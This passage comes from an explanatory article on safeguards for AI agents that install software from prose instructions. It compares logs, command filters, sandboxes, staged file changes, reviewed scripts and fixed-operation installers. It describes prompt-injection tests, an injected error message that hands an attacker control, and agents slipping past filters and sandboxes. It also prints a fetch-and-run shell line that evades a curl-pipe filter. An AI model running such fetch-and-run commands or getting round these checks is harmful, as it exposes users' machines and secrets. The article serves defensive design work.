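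Anthropic also commissioned a test from Trajectory Labs, in which none of 720 prompt injection attempts succeeded against Claude models in auto mode, while 5.83 percent succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex's equivalent mode. These attacks tried to turn the agent away from the user's task, whereas an agent that follows a hostile install document is doing what the user asked. The attacks also came from only 72 scenarios, and their writers had refined them against an older Claude model. The result is good evidence about how agents handle hostile web pages they happen to read during an installation, but weaker evidence about how they handle a hostile install document.

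### What a log proves

Agent programs keep a log of the commands they run and the output. A user can check it afterwards to see which address a file came from, whether the agent compared hashes, and whether it used administrator rights. The log is more reliable than the agent's closing summary. In 68 percent of the reports where Zhong and colleagues could tell how the agent had reacted to the harm, it carried on as if nothing had gone wrong, and one agent wrote "No problems occurred" right after erasing a file.

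The log shows that a program started and what it printed, but not what else it did. In an example from Zhong and colleagues, an agent builds a project with `cargo build`, the usual command for building Rust programs. If one of the project's packages is malicious, its build script can read the user's SSH key and change the shell's configuration, while the log contains only an ordinary build. Likewise, the `bun completions` line doesn't show everything that command did.

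A malicious program can also edit a log that the user's account can write to. A company that wants to rely on its logs should send them to another machine as the agent works. Even then, the log only helps people find and repair damage. Someone who learns from the log that a program stole their password still has to change it.

### Filters on commands

A filter compares each command with a list of rules before it runs. Monperrus, a researcher at KTH Royal Institute of Technology in Stockholm, published one for Claude Code that forbids piping a download into a shell. It uses a hook, a small program that Claude Code runs before every shell command:

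1. Claude Code passes the command to the hook.
2. The hook saves the command in a temporary file and gives it to Semgrep, a program that analyses the structure of code.
3. Semgrep looks for a pipe with `curl` or `wget` on the left and one of ten shells on the right.
4. If it finds one, the hook blocks the command and tells the agent to download the script, inspect it and then execute it.

In Monperrus's test, the hook blocked all five dangerous commands and allowed both harmless ones. It would also block the first line of Hugging Face's skill, which pipes the install script into Bash.

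The filter doesn't stop an agent that downloads a script with one command and runs it with the next. Monperrus considers the separate download an improvement because a person or the agent can then read the script on disk, but says it is "not a security guarantee". The script is still untrusted code, and nothing makes the agent read it first. The more cautious third-party skill would also pass the filter, and its `less` command doesn't pause for an agent.

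Other commands have the same effect without a pipe:

```
bash -c "$(curl -fsSL ADDRESS)"
```

The published rule wouldn't match this line, although someone could add one that does. The hook also depends on the program `jq` to extract the command from Claude Code's message. If `jq` is missing, the hook gets an empty command and allows it.

Zhong and colleagues found 52 reports in which filters failed because they checked a command's text rather than its effect. For example, a filter that blocks `rm` doesn't stop an agent from deleting the same file with Python. Filters are useful against known bad habits. Their rules are fixed, so a new model doesn't change what they block, but it may phrase its commands in ways the rules don't cover.

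### Sandboxes and staged changes

A sandbox, unlike a filter, works however the agent phrases its commands. In jedwhite's thread, linkregister suggested running prose instructions in a container or on an automated build server, and White agreed. This suits programs that will also be used there. An agent can install a project's packages inside a container, and if something goes wrong, the user can delete the container and start again.

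Other installations have to change the machine itself. Installing a graphics driver, a system-wide background service or a new operating system requires access that a sandbox is meant to block. Bun needs less access, but an agent would still have to reach GitHub and write to `~/.bun` and the shell's configuration file. Allowing changes to the configuration file is a serious exception, because the shell will run whatever is in it, outside the sandbox, the next time the user opens a terminal. The new program will normally run outside the sandbox too.

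Anthropic says sandboxes are safe but take a lot of work, because users have to configure each new capability. In 41 of Zhong and colleagues' reports, the sandbox didn't suit the task. Some sandboxes blocked ordinary builds and tests, and the agent program then offered to rerun the command without protection. Other sandboxes let the agent delete files inside the permitted area.

Zhong and colleagues built a more flexible alternative for Linux called YoloFS. The agent appears to change files as usual, but YoloFS holds the changes separately until the user accepts or discards them. After a Bun installation, the user would see a list of new files under `~/.bun` and the lines added to `.bashrc`, instead of having to predict the effects of eight commands. YoloFS can also prompt the user before a command reads a sensitive file, because discarding changes can't undo the theft of a key.

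Agents that could see the file changes noticed and undid the damage in eight of 11 tasks with hidden destructive side effects. In the other three, the changes looked to the agent like part of the job, but the user could still reject them. On 112 routine tasks, the success rate stayed at 99 percent and users had fewer questions to answer. YoloFS covers only files, so it doesn't show what a program sends over the network, and the user can't judge from a list of new files whether Bun itself is safe.

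### Having the agent write a script

Even with these checks, the agent still chooses commands during the installation. It can instead write them all in a script first, as linkregister and nobodywillobsrv proposed. Someone reviews the script and records its hash, then Bash runs it without the agent.

Even if the written instructions include shell commands, a reader can't be sure which commands will run. In the hybrid format Sébastien describes, the model can use the included commands word for word or adapt them.

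Suppose an administrator gives Koomen's Bun instructions to an agent and asks for a script for 50 Linux laptops with Intel-type processors and Bash. After some corrections, the result might look like this, where ADDRESS leads to one particular release and HASH is the hash of its zip file:

```
set -eu
[ "$(uname -sm)" = "Linux x86_64" ] || { echo "Wrong system"; exit 1; }
if ldd --version 2>&1 | grep -q musl; then echo "Needs musl build"; exit 1; fi
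tmp=$(mktemp -d)
curl -fsSL -o "$tmp/bun.zip" ADDRESS
echo "HASH  $tmp/bun.zip" | sha256sum -c -
mkdir -p ~/.bun/bin
unzip -jo "$tmp/bun.zip" -d ~/.bun/bin
chmod +x ~/.bun/bin/bun
~/.bun/bin/bun --version
grep -q BUN_INSTALL ~/.bashrc || printf '%s\n' \
  'export BUN_INSTALL="$HOME/.bun"' \
  'export PATH="$BUN_INSTALL/bin:$PATH"' >> ~/.bashrc
~/.bun/bin/bun completions || true
rm "$tmp/bun.zip"
rmdir "$tmp"
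```

The first line makes the script stop when a command fails, so a zip file with the wrong hash never gets unpacked. The script also runs Bun once before changing the shell's configuration, which would reveal a build that doesn't work on the machine.

| Decision | Agent follows the prose | Agent writes a script first |
|---|---|---|
| Which release to install | The agent chooses during each installation | The reviewer approves one address |
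| Whether the download is the right file | The agent may or may not check | The script compares it with a fixed hash |
| What to do on a musl system | The agent looks for the right build | The script stops |
| What to do if `unzip` is missing | The agent may install it or use another program | The script stops |
| What to do with an older copy of Bun | The agent may keep, move or replace it | The script replaces it |
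| Which temporary files to delete | The agent decides what "clean up" covers | The script deletes one named file and an empty folder |

The reviewer can now object to any of these decisions, such as replacing older copies of Bun, before the script reaches a laptop. The cleanup also can't repeat what happened on DocTomoe's 27th run, because `rmdir` only deletes empty folders.

The reviewer should compare the hash with one published by Bun's developers. A hash that the agent computed from its own download ensures that all 50 laptops get the same file, but not that the file came from Bun's developers.

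A second model can review the script, with the same limits as any AI review of a script. Even if a hostile document misled the model that wrote the script, any harmful command is in the text, where the reviewer can find it. The agent should only write the script at this stage. If it needs to experiment, it can use a virtual machine with no real passwords.

Replacing the model has no effect on a finished script. When Bun releases a new version, the administrator can change the address and the hash by hand, or ask a newer model for a new script and review it. But the script can't adapt to a different system. On a laptop with Alpine Linux, it gives an error message, and somebody has to produce and review another version.

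Having the agent write a script first may not be worth the trouble for a single laptop, since Bun already publishes a script. But Bun's script is long partly because it has to support every kind of machine, and a short script for one kind is much easier to read. This approach is most useful when the software's author has published only written instructions, or when many similar machines need the same installation.

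### Running the author's script first

roywiggins's proposal was to run the normal installer and bring in an agent only if it fails. In the earlier illustration, an agent damaged one in 1,000 honest installations, or about 1,000 in a million. If the author's script works on 95 percent of machines, the agent handles only 50,000 of that million and damages about 50. It would probably do worse than one in 1,000 on those machines, because they are the difficult ones, but it would still do far less damage overall. A malicious script would do as much harm as before, since the agent comes in too late to refuse it.

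The design depends on detecting when the script has failed. On Void Linux, Bun's script installs the wrong build and reports success, so nobody would call the agent. A separate check has to run after the script, such as whether `bun --version` works.

Showing the agent an error message is also risky. In 0DIN's demonstration, the error message contained an instruction for Claude Code to run the command that gave the attacker control, and a malicious installer could fail on purpose to show such a message. An agent with full permissions can also do damage that the failed script did not. It is safer to have the agent propose a correction to the script and have a person review it before running the script again. The script's author can then add the correction for everyone, so the next user with the same kind of machine doesn't need an agent.

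This design keeps most of the agent's flexibility, but installation is somewhat slower on unusual machines. Switching to a new model can change only the repairs.

### Installers with a fixed set of operations

An author can also give agents an installer that accepts only certain requests. Agama, the installer for the Linux distribution openSUSE, will do this from version 26. Agama's *The first AI-ready OS installer* (2026) announces a server that uses the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect a model to outside tools. A user can ask an assistant for openSUSE with a certain desktop, disk layout and account, and the assistant passes these choices to Agama as structured settings.

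According to Linuxiac's *openSUSE’s Agama 26 to Support Fully Automated AI-Driven Linux Installations* (2026), Agama rejects malformed or technically invalid settings. The interface doesn't give the agent a shell or direct access to disk partitioning tools. In one mode, the agent only prepares the settings, and a person approves and starts the installation. In the other, the agent can install without supervision, including formatting disks and restarting the machine. The server is off by default.

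Red Hat (2026) built a similar assistant for OpenShift, its platform for running applications across many machines. The model sends a structured request, and a server checks it against a list of permitted actions. Deleting a cluster (a group of machines that work together) isn't on the list, so the server would reject that request even if someone tricked the model into sending it. Red Hat considered letting customers connect their own agents, such as Claude Code, but decided against it because it couldn't guarantee that an outside agent would handle errors correctly or do the steps in the right order. Agama lets users choose their own agent.

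With such an installer, a reviewer can check the list of operations once and the proposed settings each time. A new model may propose different settings, but it can't add an operation. Valid settings can still be wrong. Agama can confirm that a disk exists and is large enough, but it may not detect that the disk holds the user's only copy of their photos. The mode in which a person approves the settings is therefore much safer, and that person reads one short list instead of the long series of commands that an agent with a shell would show them.

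The limits apply only to what goes through the installer, so an agent that also has a shell on the user's computer can do other things there. Somebody also has to build and maintain the interface, which makes sense for an operating system with many settings. For Bun, the choices might be little more than the version, the folder and whether to edit the shell's configuration, and a script with three options would do the same job.

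### The designs side by side

In all of these designs, the user has to trust the author, the servers that supply the files and the programs that run the commands. The second column lists who else the user has to trust.

| Design | Also trusted | What the user can check | What a new model changes | Flexibility lost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plain install script | Nobody | Every command in the script, beforehand | Nothing | Works only on machines the author planned for |
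| Plain prose document | The model, the agent program and the writers of whatever the agent reads | The request beforehand, the commands afterwards in the log | Possibly any command | None |
| Prose, with approval of each command | The same, and the user's own attention | Each command just before it runs | The commands that need approval | No unattended installation |
| Prose, with approval by a second model | The same as plain prose, and the second model | The blocking rules beforehand, the log afterwards | The commands, or how strictly the second model judges them | Harmless steps that the second model blocks |
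| Prose, with a command filter | The same as plain prose, and the filter | The filter's rules beforehand, the log afterwards | The commands, but not the rules | Harmless commands that match a rule |
| Prose, in a sandbox | The same as plain prose, and the sandbox | What the agent can reach | The commands, but not the limits | Drivers, system services and other changes to the machine itself |
| Prose, with staged changes | The same as plain prose, and the staging system | The changed files, before accepting them | The changes that need review | Little, but a person must review the result |
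| Agent writes a script, which someone reviews | The reviewer, and the agent only as far as the review misses its mistakes | Every command in the script, beforehand | Nothing, until someone asks for a new script | A different kind of machine needs a new script and review |
| Author's script first, agent after a failure | The agent, but only on machines where the script fails | Every command in the script; for repairs, whatever checks the user adds | Only the repairs | Little; unusual machines take longer |
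| Installer with fixed operations | The model, for its choice of settings | The list of operations and the proposed settings | The settings, but not the operations | Anything the installer doesn't offer |
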